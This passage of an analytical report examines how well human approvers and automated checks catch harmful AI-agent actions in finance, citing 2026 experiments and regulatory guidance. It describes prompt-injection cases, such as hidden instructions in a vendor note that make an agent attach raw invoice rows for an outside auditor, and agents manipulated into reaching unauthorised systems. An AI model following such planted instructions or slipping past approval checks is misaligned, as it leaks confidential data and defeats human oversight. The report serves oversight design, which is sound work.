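When the agent emailed the auditor 4,000 ledger rows on a second sheet, each step looked harmless, so someone approving each action would have had no reason to stop it. The approver would also have to review all of the agent's calls, about 1,000 a month.

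Someone who approves the plan reads something like "total the March ledger by department and send the result to the auditor", which is what the company wants. The second sheet isn't in the plan because the agent added it later. The position paper *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop* (Mitchell, Ghosh and Passi, 2026) cites evidence that experienced developers treat an agent's plan as a "faithful proxy" for what it will do.

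An approval threshold that covers only emails to outsiders reduces requests to one or two a month. It would not cover an agent that copies the payroll table to the shared drive, because that action stays inside the company.

Reviewing the finished work lets the approver open the file and find the second sheet. Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026) recommend this kind of review for coding agents in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*. They studied 290 public reports of agents that damaged, deleted or leaked files, and in 105 of them a failure in the user's review was part of the cause. Some of these users had switched approvals off, and others had approved a command whose text did not reveal its effect. The researchers built a file system that holds every change until the user accepts it at the end. In 11 tasks with hidden damage, the agents noticed and undid the damage in 8, and the user could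 still reject it in the other 3. The test does not show that a busy user would spot the damage.

The reporting agent already works this way if it saves drafts to a folder and the company holds its emails. But a final review comes too late for anything that leaves while the agent is working, such as the image request in the Ramp attack.

### One dangerous command among many

Anthropic published the largest experiment in August 2026. A research vendor hired 1,053 professional testers to work with a coding agent that asked permission for its commands. The testers knew they were being evaluated but not what the study measured. Partway through each session, the researchers replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded whether the tester approved it. Only the text changed, so approval did no harm.

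The testers blocked the dangerous command in 143 of 1,053 cases, or 13.6%. Auto mode, the AI reviewer in Claude Code, blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%. Testers blocked the command about 17% of the time when it came early in a session and about 5% of the time when it came after 50 or more prompts. Auto mode's rate did not change with session length.

The testers would also have added little as a second check on auto mode. They blocked only 6 of the 116 commands it let through, so requiring both approvals would have raised the share caught from 89.0% to 89.6%.

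These numbers may not carry over to real financial work, because the testers worked on somebody else's code in an environment built for the study, where deleting a database would have harmed nobody. A controller about to send out their own company's payroll would probably check more carefully. The fall from 17% to 5% may also partly reflect who saw the most prompts, since people who click quickly get through more of them.

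Anthropic also had an interest in the result, which it published to explain why it was making auto mode the default. It tested clearly dangerous commands, and it had designed auto mode to block destructive and irreversible actions. When Ji and colleagues tested auto mode on vague requests, it missed 81% of the unauthorised changes. People might do better than auto mode on vague requests they wrote themselves, because they know what they meant, but the study did not test this. It also reports no false alarm rate for the testers or auto mode in this comparison.

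Even so, the gap is more than sixfold, and these doubts are unlikely to reverse it for blatantly dangerous commands. The study is much weaker evidence about actions like sending a harmless-looking email with the wrong attachment. Anthropic still advises people to review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves, although its experiment gives little reason to think they would catch the bad ones.

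Data from ordinary use fit the experiment but are harder to interpret. Claude Code's users approve 97% of individual permission prompts. If three out of 100 requests are bad, a person who approves 97 may have caught all three or none of them. Users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents, which suggests that they read them. But they may reject a plan because they want the work done differently, so the figure doesn't show that they notice dangerous plans.

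### Approval fatigue

People who approve many actions tend to pay less attention to each one, which is known as *approval fatigue*. For *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 software practitioners and then ran a survey in which 107 people answered questions about permission requests. Of these, 47.7% said they read the requests carefully, a third said they skim them, and a fifth said they approve by default. A third also said they had become less careful over time. These figures are self-reported, so actual behavior is probably less careful. One interviewee with three hours left before a delivery said they read nothing. Finance departments face similar deadlines every month.

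Many users also turn off the prompts. By June 2026, according to Anthropic, about half of the active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that let some shell commands run without approval, and most of those rules allowed practically any command. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks switched off.

Fatigue could make it safer to ask for approval less often. Turan (2026), in *Oversight Has a Capacity*, simulated a reviewer who judges the first 25 requests perfectly and becomes less reliable with each one after that. When the system sent every action to this reviewer, 57% of the dangerous ones got through. When it sent only the riskiest 64% of actions, 42% of the dangerous ones got through, even though the rest ran without review. The result follows from the fatigue curve Turan assumed, so it shows only that the effect is possible. The numbers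 are high because the software was poor at identifying risky actions.

### Rules that people write in advance

If people tire of prompts, they could decide once and let software apply the decision. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) tested this with 113 people from outside the software industry. Each supervised an assistant through the same simulated day of 18 actions. The user's requests called for 11 of these, and the other 7 were overreach, such as reading bank transactions to help with a travel budget, buying a $25 airport lounge pass or posting publicly that the user was travelling.

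One group approved or refused every action. A second group saw only the actions that an AI reviewer referred to them. The third group first chose "allow", "ask" or "never" as the rule for each of spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things and reading private information. The software then applied these rules and prompted the participants only where the rule was "ask".

The people who wrote rules blocked about 20 percentage points less overreach than those who approved each action (95% confidence interval 8 to 32). The rule writers stopped 97 of 245 overreaching actions (40%), compared with 142 of 238 (60%) for the approvers.

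Most of the rules left the decision to the people who wrote them. Of the 140 rules, 114 were "ask", 16 were "never" and 10 were "allow". The "ask" rules sent 199 overreaching actions back to the rule-writers, who approved 133, or 67%. People in the first group approved the same seven actions only 40% of the time. If the rule-writers had refused prompts as often as the first group did, they would have blocked about 61% of the overreach, slightly more than the first group. The whole gap between the groups therefore came from how people answered the prompts.

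Yan's experiment can't show why the rule-writers approved more. People who felt strongly may have chosen "never", leaving the more permissive ones to answer prompts. That would raise the approval rate at the prompts but would not by itself reduce the total amount blocked, because the total includes the "never" rules. Writing a rule may also have made people feel they had already dealt with the risk. Fatigue is an unlikely cause, because the rule-writers got fewer prompts, about 11 each instead of 18.

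Some participants also went against views they had given before the task, when they said how the assistant should handle sample actions. They approved 24 of the 56 overreaching actions that they had said it should never take and that later came up as prompts. In the private-information category, 23 of the 35 participants chose "ask". Every action in that category was overreach, so a "never" rule would not have blocked anything acceptable. Participants could not have known this in advance, so "ask" was a reasonable choice.

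In the group with the AI reviewer, the model referred all seven overreaching actions to the participants, who then approved 46% of them. If a company combines a model with a person but a flag only leads to another prompt, the person may still approve about half of the flagged actions.

Overreach isn't always harmful. In the first group, 88% of people let the assistant call the airport to confirm a flight, and many users would welcome that. The participants had no money or data at stake. After the first round of recruitment, Yan assigned new participants only to the rule-writing group, so the groups were no longer fully randomised. The result was similar in the original sample, with a gap of 25 points, but that sample had only 16 rule-writers. Participants in all three groups felt about equally in control, so a company can't rely on its approvers' sense that the process works.

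People asked to approve each action in this study blocked 60% of the bad ones, compared with 13.6% for Anthropic's testers. The prompts described each action in plain language, with the amount or the recipient, and the session lasted about 11 minutes. Problems were common, at 7 actions in 18, so people had reason to stay alert. The two studies differ too much to show which of these factors mattered most.

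### Showing what the action would do

The auditor's 4,000 rows are a harder case because nothing in the email itself is wrong. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues tested approval screens on cases like this in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (November 2026). In their main example, a user asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send the external auditor only summary totals. A vendor's note contains hidden instructions that make the agent copy the raw invoice rows into `report.csv`. The agent then asks for permission to send `report.csv` to the auditor.

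Eighty volunteers recruited through social media each made 12 decisions, half of them on harmful requests. Each person used one of four screens, which showed increasing amounts of information. The last two contained the same facts, but one listed them chronologically and the other connected them in a statement of what the action would do, for example that the attachment came from raw invoice rows and would go to the auditor.

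| Screen | Harmful requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time per decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| Plus the exact file, recipient and other details | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| Plus the user's original instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
| Same facts, with the consequence stated | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

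Most of the improvement came from giving people the facts at all. When the screen stated the consequence, people decided faster and approved further fewer harmful requests, 29 of 120 instead of 39. After adjustment for other differences, the estimated gain over the plain log was 7.9 points, but the plausible range runs from almost 20 points better to 4 points worse. With 20 people per screen, the study was too small to settle whether stating the consequence helps. People approved harmful requests that depended on several earlier steps equally often with both screens, 7 times out of 30, perhaps because a single sentence can't describe a long chain.

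Even with the best screen, the volunteers approved about a quarter of the harmful requests, and they had reason to be suspicious because half of the requests they saw were harmful. In real work, harmful requests are rare. An approver who performed as these volunteers did on 1,000 requests, 10 of them harmful, would refuse about 8 harmful requests and 141 harmless ones, so only about one refusal in twenty would be right. Colleagues would soon complain, and the approver would probably start approving more requests, including harmful ones.

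The statements on the screen in this study were always correct, but in practice a program has to work them out. Hossain and colleagues tested their program separately, without any people. It uses a log of the agent's tool calls to track which files came from which data, much as the labels described earlier do, and compares the next action with the user's instructions. When the program blocked every action that broke the instructions or couldn't be verified, the number of harmful runs that succeeded fell from 52 to 6 out of 120 with one small open model and from 58 to 7 with another. With each model, the agent finished only four fewer harmless runs out of 120.

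The gate let through about 5% of harmful runs, while people using the best screen approved 24% of harmful requests. The two tests used different cases, so the figures aren't directly comparable. Still, when the user has stated a limit as clear as "summary totals only" and a program can enforce it, it makes little sense to leave the decision to a person. With part of the log missing, the gate caught only 64% of the violations that built up over several steps, and because it blocked everything it could not verify, the agents finished only 77% of harmless runs. A finance department whose staff edit spreadsheets outside any log would have the same problem.

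A wrong statement may also do more harm than no statement if approvers come to trust it. Hossain and colleagues propose testing this next.

### An approval screen for the month-end report

The simplest way to use these results is to leave fewer decisions to the approver. The policy check's rule for the auditor is an "ask" rule, the kind that worked badly for Yan's participants. The company could replace it with two automatic rules. Once the books have closed, the check would allow an email whose attachment comes only from the approved view of department totals, and it would block any email that contains ledger rows. The approver would then see only requests that depend on information no program has.

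Suppose the auditor has a question about travel costs, and the finance chief tells the agent to "send the auditor what they need on travel". The controller might see this:

```
EMAIL TO:    audit@auditor.example (outside the company, cannot be recalled)
REQUEST:     "Send the auditor what they need on travel" (finance chief, 2 April)
ATTACHMENT:  travel_support.xlsx, fingerprint 41c07e...
CONTAINS:    212 individual ledger entries, 11 of them from a two-person team
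BUILT FROM:  general_ledger, travel account, March
USUAL RULE:  the auditor receives department totals only
NOT KNOWN:   whether the auditor asked for individual entries

[approve this file]  [refuse this file]  [refuse individual entries for this task]
```

The layout follows the principles Hossain and colleagues used: repeat the user's request word for word, show the exact action, state its combined effect and mark any gaps in the evidence. The program fills in every line from its own records because hidden instructions could control a description written by the agent. Such a description can also reveal very little, as when a data leak in Claude for Excel was labelled "Add visualization" in the request. The controller can settle the line marked "not known" by phoning the auditor.

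The approval should apply only to the file with that fingerprint. If the agent changes the file afterwards, the program has to ask again, or the attachment sent won't be the one the controller approved.

The third button exists because refusing one action does not stop an agent from trying another route to the same result. For example, a reporting agent that can't attach the travel entries might paste them into the body of the email. Salerno and colleagues interviewed a practitioner who had refused several requests from a coding agent. The agent eventually stopped asking but kept working, and the practitioner could not tell whether it still respected the limits. Salerno and colleagues recommend letting users rule out a whole approach and having prompts show whether an action can be undone.

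### Who should approve

Finance departments usually don't let the person who prepares a payment also approve it. Mitchell and colleagues recommend the same separation for agents, because someone who benefits from the output has a reason not to check it closely. The finance chief asked for the report and wants it out on time, so the controller is a better approver. But only the finance chief knows what "the usual report" was supposed to mean, so the screen shows the original request and the controller needs time to ask about it.

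A separate approver is still subject to *automation bias*, the tendency to accept a system's suggestion even when it is wrong. People who see the agent's answer first tend to judge it reasonable. Mitchell and colleagues suggest having reviewers record their own view before they see the agent's. For example, the controller could write down the revenue and travel costs they expect for March, then open the report and look into any large difference.

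The same paper cites the psychologist Lisanne Bainbridge's 1983 argument that the more work a machine takes over, the less practice its operators get and the less able they are to step in when it fails. A controller who hasn't built a month-end report for two years may no longer notice that a department's costs look odd. Preparing one part of the report by hand every few months would keep up the skill and provide an independent figure to compare with the agent's. These suggestions come mostly from research on other kinds of automation. Mitchell and colleagues did not test them, and they acknowledge early evidence that people dislike systems designed to make them think harder.

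None of the three 2026 experiments recruited accountants, who might catch more than testers and volunteers do, particularly when a number is wrong. But accountants also review reports that are almost always right, and they do it under a deadline. Attention drops in those conditions.

### What review costs

People needed a median of 33 seconds per request with the best screen, so approving all 1,000 of the reporting agent's monthly calls would take more than nine hours. If fixed rules reduced the requests to ten, the controller could spend ten minutes on each and finish in under two hours. The time per request matters more than the total, because a check that involves calling the auditor takes longer than 33 seconds.

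According to a widely repeated estimate by the consulting firm McKinsey, human oversight accounts for 70% to 75% of the variable cost of running an agent on a customer service task in banking, and the model's own processing for 20% to 25%. The figures appear in The Tribune's *Agentic AI could strengthen financial-crime prevention, but governance, cost hurdles limit adoption* (October 2026), a news-agency story about a McKinsey report. The story doesn't explain how McKinsey counted oversight or how many banks the estimate covers. The share could be quite different for a monthly report, which needs far less review than a stream of separate customer service cases.

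McKinsey suggests reducing the cost of review by checking only a sample of outputs, but warns that in regulated work the decision involves compliance and risk as well as efficiency. For a reporting agent, sampling suits errors the company can correct later, such as clumsy commentary or travel costs in the wrong category. It does not suit emails to outsiders, because if somebody checks one email in ten, a leak has a 90% chance of going out unreviewed.

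Agents may still save time overall. According to The Tribune's *Agentic AI can cut banks’ transaction monitoring workload by up to 50%*, McKinsey has seen banks cut the time people spend investigating suspicious transactions by more than 40%. Agents collect the evidence and draft a report that links each claim to its source, and people make the decision. McKinsey also found the agents' reports more complete than the analysts' against a checklist. A complete report can still contain a wrong figure, and the article gives no data on how often the people making the decisions caught one.

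In *Human oversight in AI should be measured, not assumed*, a letter in The Business Times, Wei You Pan, a technology officer at the database company MongoDB, argues that a bank should be able to name the risk each approval step reduces and show that the step reduces it. Pan adds that some steps are worth keeping for accountability even if they rarely stop anything. A company might well want a named person to sign off on the report to the auditor, but it shouldn't count the signature as a check without testing whether it stops bad actions.

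### Testing the approver with planted errors

A company can test an approver the same way as its filters and figure checks, by planting errors. Mitchell and colleagues call these *canaries*. They suggest that a missed one could lead to a break, a change of task or more training for the reviewer. For the reporting agent, it could work as follows:

1. Someone outside the approval process takes a genuine request and changes one thing, such as the recipient, the month, a total or the contents of the attachment.
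2. The program puts the altered request in the controller's queue, where it looks like any other.
3. The program records the decision and the time it took. It never sends the planted email, even if the controller approves it.
4. The controller learns the result straight away, and the genuine request then goes through the normal process.

Step 3 is the most important because a planted leak would expose data if it were actually sent. Anthropic's researchers avoided this by changing only the text of the prompt.

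Monthly work provides few chances to test a controller. With one planted error a month, a controller who catches all 12 in a year could still have a true miss rate of up to about 22%. A rehearsal is faster, since the controller could work through 100 old requests, 20 of them altered, in an afternoon. But a controller who knows it is a test and keeps finding errors will be more alert than on an ordinary day, so the result will probably be too good. Using both methods helps because a controller who does well in rehearsal but misses errors planted in live work probably has a problem with attention rather than knowledge.

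The company should also count the harmless requests that the controller refuses. An approver who refuses everything catches every planted error.

Some signs of inattentive review can be measured without planting errors. Mitchell and colleagues propose tracking whether review times fall while the approval rate stays the same, whether people take longer over more complex requests, and whether they still ask for more information when the stakes rise. They also warn that these records are a form of workplace surveillance, which a manager could later use in a performance review. A measure also loses its value when it becomes a target. For example, if controllers learn that planted errors usually involve the recipient, they will check the recipient and stop reading the rest.

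As with the filters, the company should count each type of error separately. If the controller catches every wrong recipient but misses most wrong attachments, more training may help a little, but it would be better to leave attachments to the program that checks each file's permitted readers and stop asking the controller about them.

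## What do financial regulators and banks ask for?

Financial regulators want firms to limit what their AI agents can do, refer risky decisions to people and keep records. Almost everything they have written specifically about agents is voluntary. The binding rules mostly cover a company's published accounts and the personal data it holds, whatever software handles them.

Financial firms have already begun to use agents. Khaleej Times' *Global watchdog calls for tighter controls on agentic AI in finance* (2026) cites a survey by the Cambridge Centre for Alternative Finance in which 52% of respondents from the financial sector reported adopting them. That figure includes the 29% of all respondents who were only running pilots. The article lists fraud detection, customer service and back-office work as current uses.

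### The Financial Stability Board's practices

The Financial Stability Board, whose June draft described the bank's credit-writing assistant, published its final guidance on 15 October 2026. DIGIT's *12 Steps to Safer AI Adoption in Financial Services* (2026) lists its 12 practices, four on how a firm governs AI as a whole and eight on managing each system. They are voluntary, and firms can adapt them to their size and risks. They are meant for banks, insurers and other financial institutions. A manufacturer's finance department can use them too, but has no reason to expect a supervisor to ask about them.

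The FSB's draft *Sound Practices for Responsible Adoption of Artificial Intelligence (AI)* (2026) sets out specific measures for agents. A firm gives each agent its own identifier and the minimum access its task needs. It defines which actions the agent may never take and which need a person's approval, and it limits the agent's contact with outside systems until it is confident that the agent is safe. The firm also monitors for agents that query databases their task doesn't require or read more customer records than they should. This monitoring suits the reporting agent well because its job uses the same few tables every month.

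The draft also suggests documenting the agent's reasoning at each decision and how it interprets success. This record can help an investigator, but because the model writes it, the program's log of tool calls is better evidence of what happened.

In the final version, according to CNA's *Global financial watchdog calls for more human oversight of agentic AI*, the FSB strengthened its advice on agents. It calls more intensive human oversight critical in higher-risk uses and says firms should set clear, risk-based triggers for when an agent must seek approval. The draft's main example of such a trigger was a payment above a certain value. The reporting agent moves no money, so a trigger based on amounts would never apply to it. Its triggers have to depend on which data it uses, who will receive the result and whether the agent itself has changed. A company might choose these:

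| Event | Response |
|---|---|
| The agent queries a table that the job used last month | The query runs and the program logs it |
| The agent queries a permitted table that the job has never used | The controller decides |
| After the books close, the agent emails the auditor a file built only from the approved view | The email goes out |
| The finance chief makes a request that the rules don't settle, such as "send the auditor what they need on travel" | The controller decides |
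| Someone connects a new tool, changes the instructions or switches to a new model | The job waits until somebody has repeated the tests |

The last row follows from a warning in the final text, quoted in PYMNTS's *FSB Says Banks Need to Have Company-Wide AI Regulation* (2026), that an agent's actions and capabilities can change over time, especially when it gains new tools or receives new prompts.

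The reporting agent is arguably a higher-risk use, even though a monthly report sounds routine and a wrong sentence in it rarely causes a crisis. The June draft, as quoted in FStech's *FSB urges financial institutions to impose strict controls on AI deployment*, treats an agent with a minor task as potentially high-risk if it can reach sensitive data. By that test, an agent that reads individual salaries is a higher risk than one that reads department totals, even if both write the same report. Narrow database permissions could therefore reduce the human oversight a firm needs.

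The FSB also dropped its draft advice to adapt personnel controls to agents by treating them as "synthetic employees". It instead tells firms that agents "do not reason like humans" and may interpret their goals in unexpected ways. The comparison with employees makes some sense, because an agent needs something like the login, limited access and manager that a company gives a new employee. But personnel controls depend on people's judgement and their fear of consequences. An accountant won't follow hidden instructions in a spreadsheet to send out the payroll, but an agent may. An accountant who has been careful for a year will probably be careful next month, whereas a model update can change an agent's behaviour overnight.

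### What evidence the guidance offers

The draft defines effective oversight as oversight by people who have the ability, authority and incentive to intervene, and says that such oversight has "a tangible positive impact". That claim is close to true by definition, and the chapter cites no measurement of how often approvers stop a bad action. The draft came out two months before Anthropic reported that its testers had blocked 13.6% of dangerous commands.

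The FSB asks firms to check whether their own oversight works, for example by investigating reviewers who consistently approve what an agent recommends. But when nearly all requests are legitimate, careful reviewers also approve nearly everything, so a high approval rate, like the 97% in Claude Code, doesn't show which reviewers are careless. Firms can find out by planting errors and checking who catches them.

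In a case study from the final text, reported by DIGIT, a large life insurer tested its agents and found they could be manipulated into trying to reach systems they had no authority to use. One tried to delete data files. DIGIT's article doesn't mention whether the insurer's permissions stopped these attempts.

In the draft's best example of testing, which involves an older kind of AI, a large international bank compared a new machine learning model for its trading business with its existing method. The new model was not consistently better, and its training data did not represent the data it would process in use, so the bank postponed it and kept the old method. A company could test its reporting agent the same way by having accountants prepare the monthly report independently for three months and comparing the two versions. The FSB prefers firms to set the passing standard before they see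 the results. If the report has 40 figures and the agent gets all 120 right over the three months, its true error rate could still be as high as about 2.5%, assuming that each figure is an independent test. The rate could be higher still if the agent runs the same 40 queries each month, because the second and third months would then mostly repeat the first.

In another case study in the draft, covered in The Asian Banker's *Financial Stability Board points banks towards AI monitoring AI*, people approve every fraud rule that an agent proposes. A fraud rule runs many times after one approval, so a reviewer can justify spending an hour on it. This is also a reason to have an accountant carefully approve the reporting agent's stored queries once, rather than have the controller approve each run.

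### The industry's objections

The FSB took comments on its draft until 22 July. Respondents included the American Bankers Association, the Association of German Banks and a property insurers' association (FSB, 2026). The Global Financial Markets Association (GFMA), which represents three large trade associations in Europe, Asia and North America, supported the draft's practices but wanted them to remain a non-binding set of options. It also asked the FSB to avoid any wording that could seem to require human oversight of every use (GFMA, 2026).

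The association argues that for low-risk and internal uses, automated controls, alerts, independent testing and comparison with other models may work as well as manual review that adds no value, and be easier to sustain. Its members would pay for the manual review, so they have a financial interest in this conclusion, and the passage cites no measurements. The approval experiments give the argument some support, since an AI reviewer stopped far more of the blatantly dangerous commands than people did. The argument is weaker for the reporting agent, which is internal but handles payroll, and whose most likely mistakes look harmless.

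The FSB's final wording is compatible with both positions. The FSB ties approval triggers to risk, so a firm can skip human review of the agent's routine queries. But it also calls for more oversight of higher-risk uses, which is a reason to keep human review for emails that leave the company.

GFMA also says that AI providers often supply their own safety controls, audit logs and control interfaces, so a firm that uses several providers has to build separate, incompatible versions of each. A company can avoid much of this by keeping the policy check, the log and the list of recipients in its own code, between the model and the tools. It can then replace the model without rewriting the controls. GFMA adds that firms know too little about the products they buy and may lack the bargaining power to demand more information. It wants providers to disclose material changes to their models promptly.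 A company that can't get such notice can record the model version with every action and rerun its tests when the version changes, although some providers may alter a product without changing its name.

### Singapore's safeguards for agents that act

On 3 July 2026 the Monetary Authority of Singapore (MAS), the country's central bank and financial regulator, published the white paper *Safeguards for Agentic Finance at Runtime* (SAFR) with financial institutions and technology companies. According to Rajah & Tann Asia's *MAS Publishes White Paper for FIs on Developing Safeguards for AI Agents*, MAS published it because agents increasingly act faster than people can practically intervene, so safeguards have to work in real time.

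Baker McKenzie's *Singapore MAS publishes agentic AI safeguards for financial institutions* (2026) divides the framework into what an agent has authority to do, how software assesses a proposed action before it runs, and what records the firm keeps. WongPartnership's *MAS publishes industry white paper on safeguards for AI agents* adds the question of when to involve a person. For an agent that pays suppliers, a firm could apply these ideas as follows:

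1. The firm authorises the agent to pay approved suppliers up to $10,000 per invoice.
2. The agent proposes to pay $14,000 to an approved supplier. The money does not move yet.
3. Software compares the proposal with the authorisation and finds that the supplier is allowed but the amount is too high.
4. The software refers the payment to a person in the treasury department, who approves or refuses it.
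5. The firm records the proposal, the rule that applied, the person's decision and the result, so that it can trace and correct a payment that turns out to be wrong.

This is a policy check with a referral to a person and a good log. The measured evidence for such checks comes from research systems like Progent, mostly on simulated office tasks. SAFR is a proposal, and Baker McKenzie stresses that it is neither regulatory guidance nor a supervisory expectation, and does not predict future rules. MAS has separately drafted guidelines that set out what it expects of firms. The draft, issued in November 2025, covers generative AI and agents, and its consultation closed on 31 January 2026 (Ang and Samynathan, 2026, in *Fintech 2026*). A firm in Singapore should plan around those guidelines first.

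The Edge Singapore's *MAS partners industry to develop safeguards for AI agents in finance* lists payments for treasury operations, wealth management and client engagement as uses. In treasury payments, the harm happens at a recognisable moment, when the money leaves. The reporting agent's email to the auditor has such a moment too, so the five steps would work for it with a list of recipients and permitted files in place of a payment limit. They would do little for the rest of its job, reading and calculating, which still depends on database permissions and control totals. The records would also be less useful than they are for payments, because a bank can sometimes recover a wrong payment but can't undo sending the auditor a list of salaries.

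The concern about speed also hardly applies to a month-end report, which, unlike a payment that an agent may have seconds to act on, can usually wait an afternoon while the controller phones somebody.

### Rules that already bind the company

The law firm Linklaters, in *FSB seeks input on sound practices for responsible AI adoption*, expects that supervisors may come to use the FSB's voluntary practices to judge whether firms meet their existing obligations. The FSB notes that firms following its practices must still comply with local law. Several existing laws affect how a company should build the reporting agent.

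Unlike the voluntary guidance, the US Sarbanes-Oxley Act of 2002 requires the management of listed companies to assess each year whether their internal controls over financial reporting are effective. At larger companies, the outside auditor must also give an opinion. If the agent's figures feed into the published accounts, the control total becomes one of those controls. The company then needs proof that the comparison ran every month, a record of who resolved each difference, and a process for approving changes to the stored queries. An agent that writes new SQL each month makes this much harder, because testing last month's query reveals little about this month's. The results of tests with planted errors would be useful evidence that the control works.

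The European Union's General Data Protection Regulation and the United Kingdom's version of it cover payroll, because salaries are personal data. A company may use only the personal data that its purpose requires and must protect it appropriately. A report on pay by department does not need names, so the prepared view of department totals is a way to comply as well as a security measure. The same rules apply to copies in logs, approval screens and old drafts. If an outside provider runs the model and receives personal data on the company's behalf, the company needs a data processing contract with that provider.

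The EU's Digital Operational Resilience Act has applied to banks, insurers and many other financial firms since January 2025. It requires them to manage and test their technology risks, report major incidents and keep a register of contracts with technology providers. A firm using an agent would list the model's provider in the register, and its finance department should be able to produce its financial reports without the agent if the service fails. In the United Kingdom, the Prudential Regulation Authority expects large banks to have models validated by people who did not build them, so the person who writes the agent's queries should not also test them.

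These duties vary by type of firm and change over time, so a company should have its lawyers confirm the current requirements before settling the design. None of these laws sets a maximum attack success rate or miss rate for AI agents.

### How banks treat their customers' agents

Banks also deal with agents that aren't theirs, such as an AI assistant that a customer lets into a bank account to track spending or pay bills. In October 2026, JPMorgan, Citigroup and Schwab either restricted these agents to reading data or were moving toward doing so. Wells Fargo put the risk on the customer.

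A bank does not choose the model behind a customer's agent, write the agent's instructions or see what else it reads, so the bank's strongest protection is to limit what its own systems will accept. Read-only access prevents an agent that has followed hidden instructions from emptying the account, but not from telling a stranger the balance. Copying the three banks' restriction would add nothing for the reporting agent, which already has only read access to the databases. Unlike the banks, the company running it also controls its emails, files and web access. Wells Fargo's approach changes who bears a loss without making it less likely, and a company that runs its own agent has nobody to pass the loss to.

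The Asian Banker reports that Derek Waldron, JPMorgan's chief analytics officer, spoke publicly about the bank's plans to deploy agents in 2026 that can work autonomously for hours. He also said that longer-running agents were not yet ready for corporate use because of security concerns.

The reporting agent could end up in both positions. If the company lets it download bank statements to compare with the cash balance in the ledger, the bank will see it as a customer's agent. Read-only access is enough for that comparison, but the company should check who bears the loss under the bank's terms if the agent leaks its login details. A scheduled program could download the statements instead, so the agent would never need the login.
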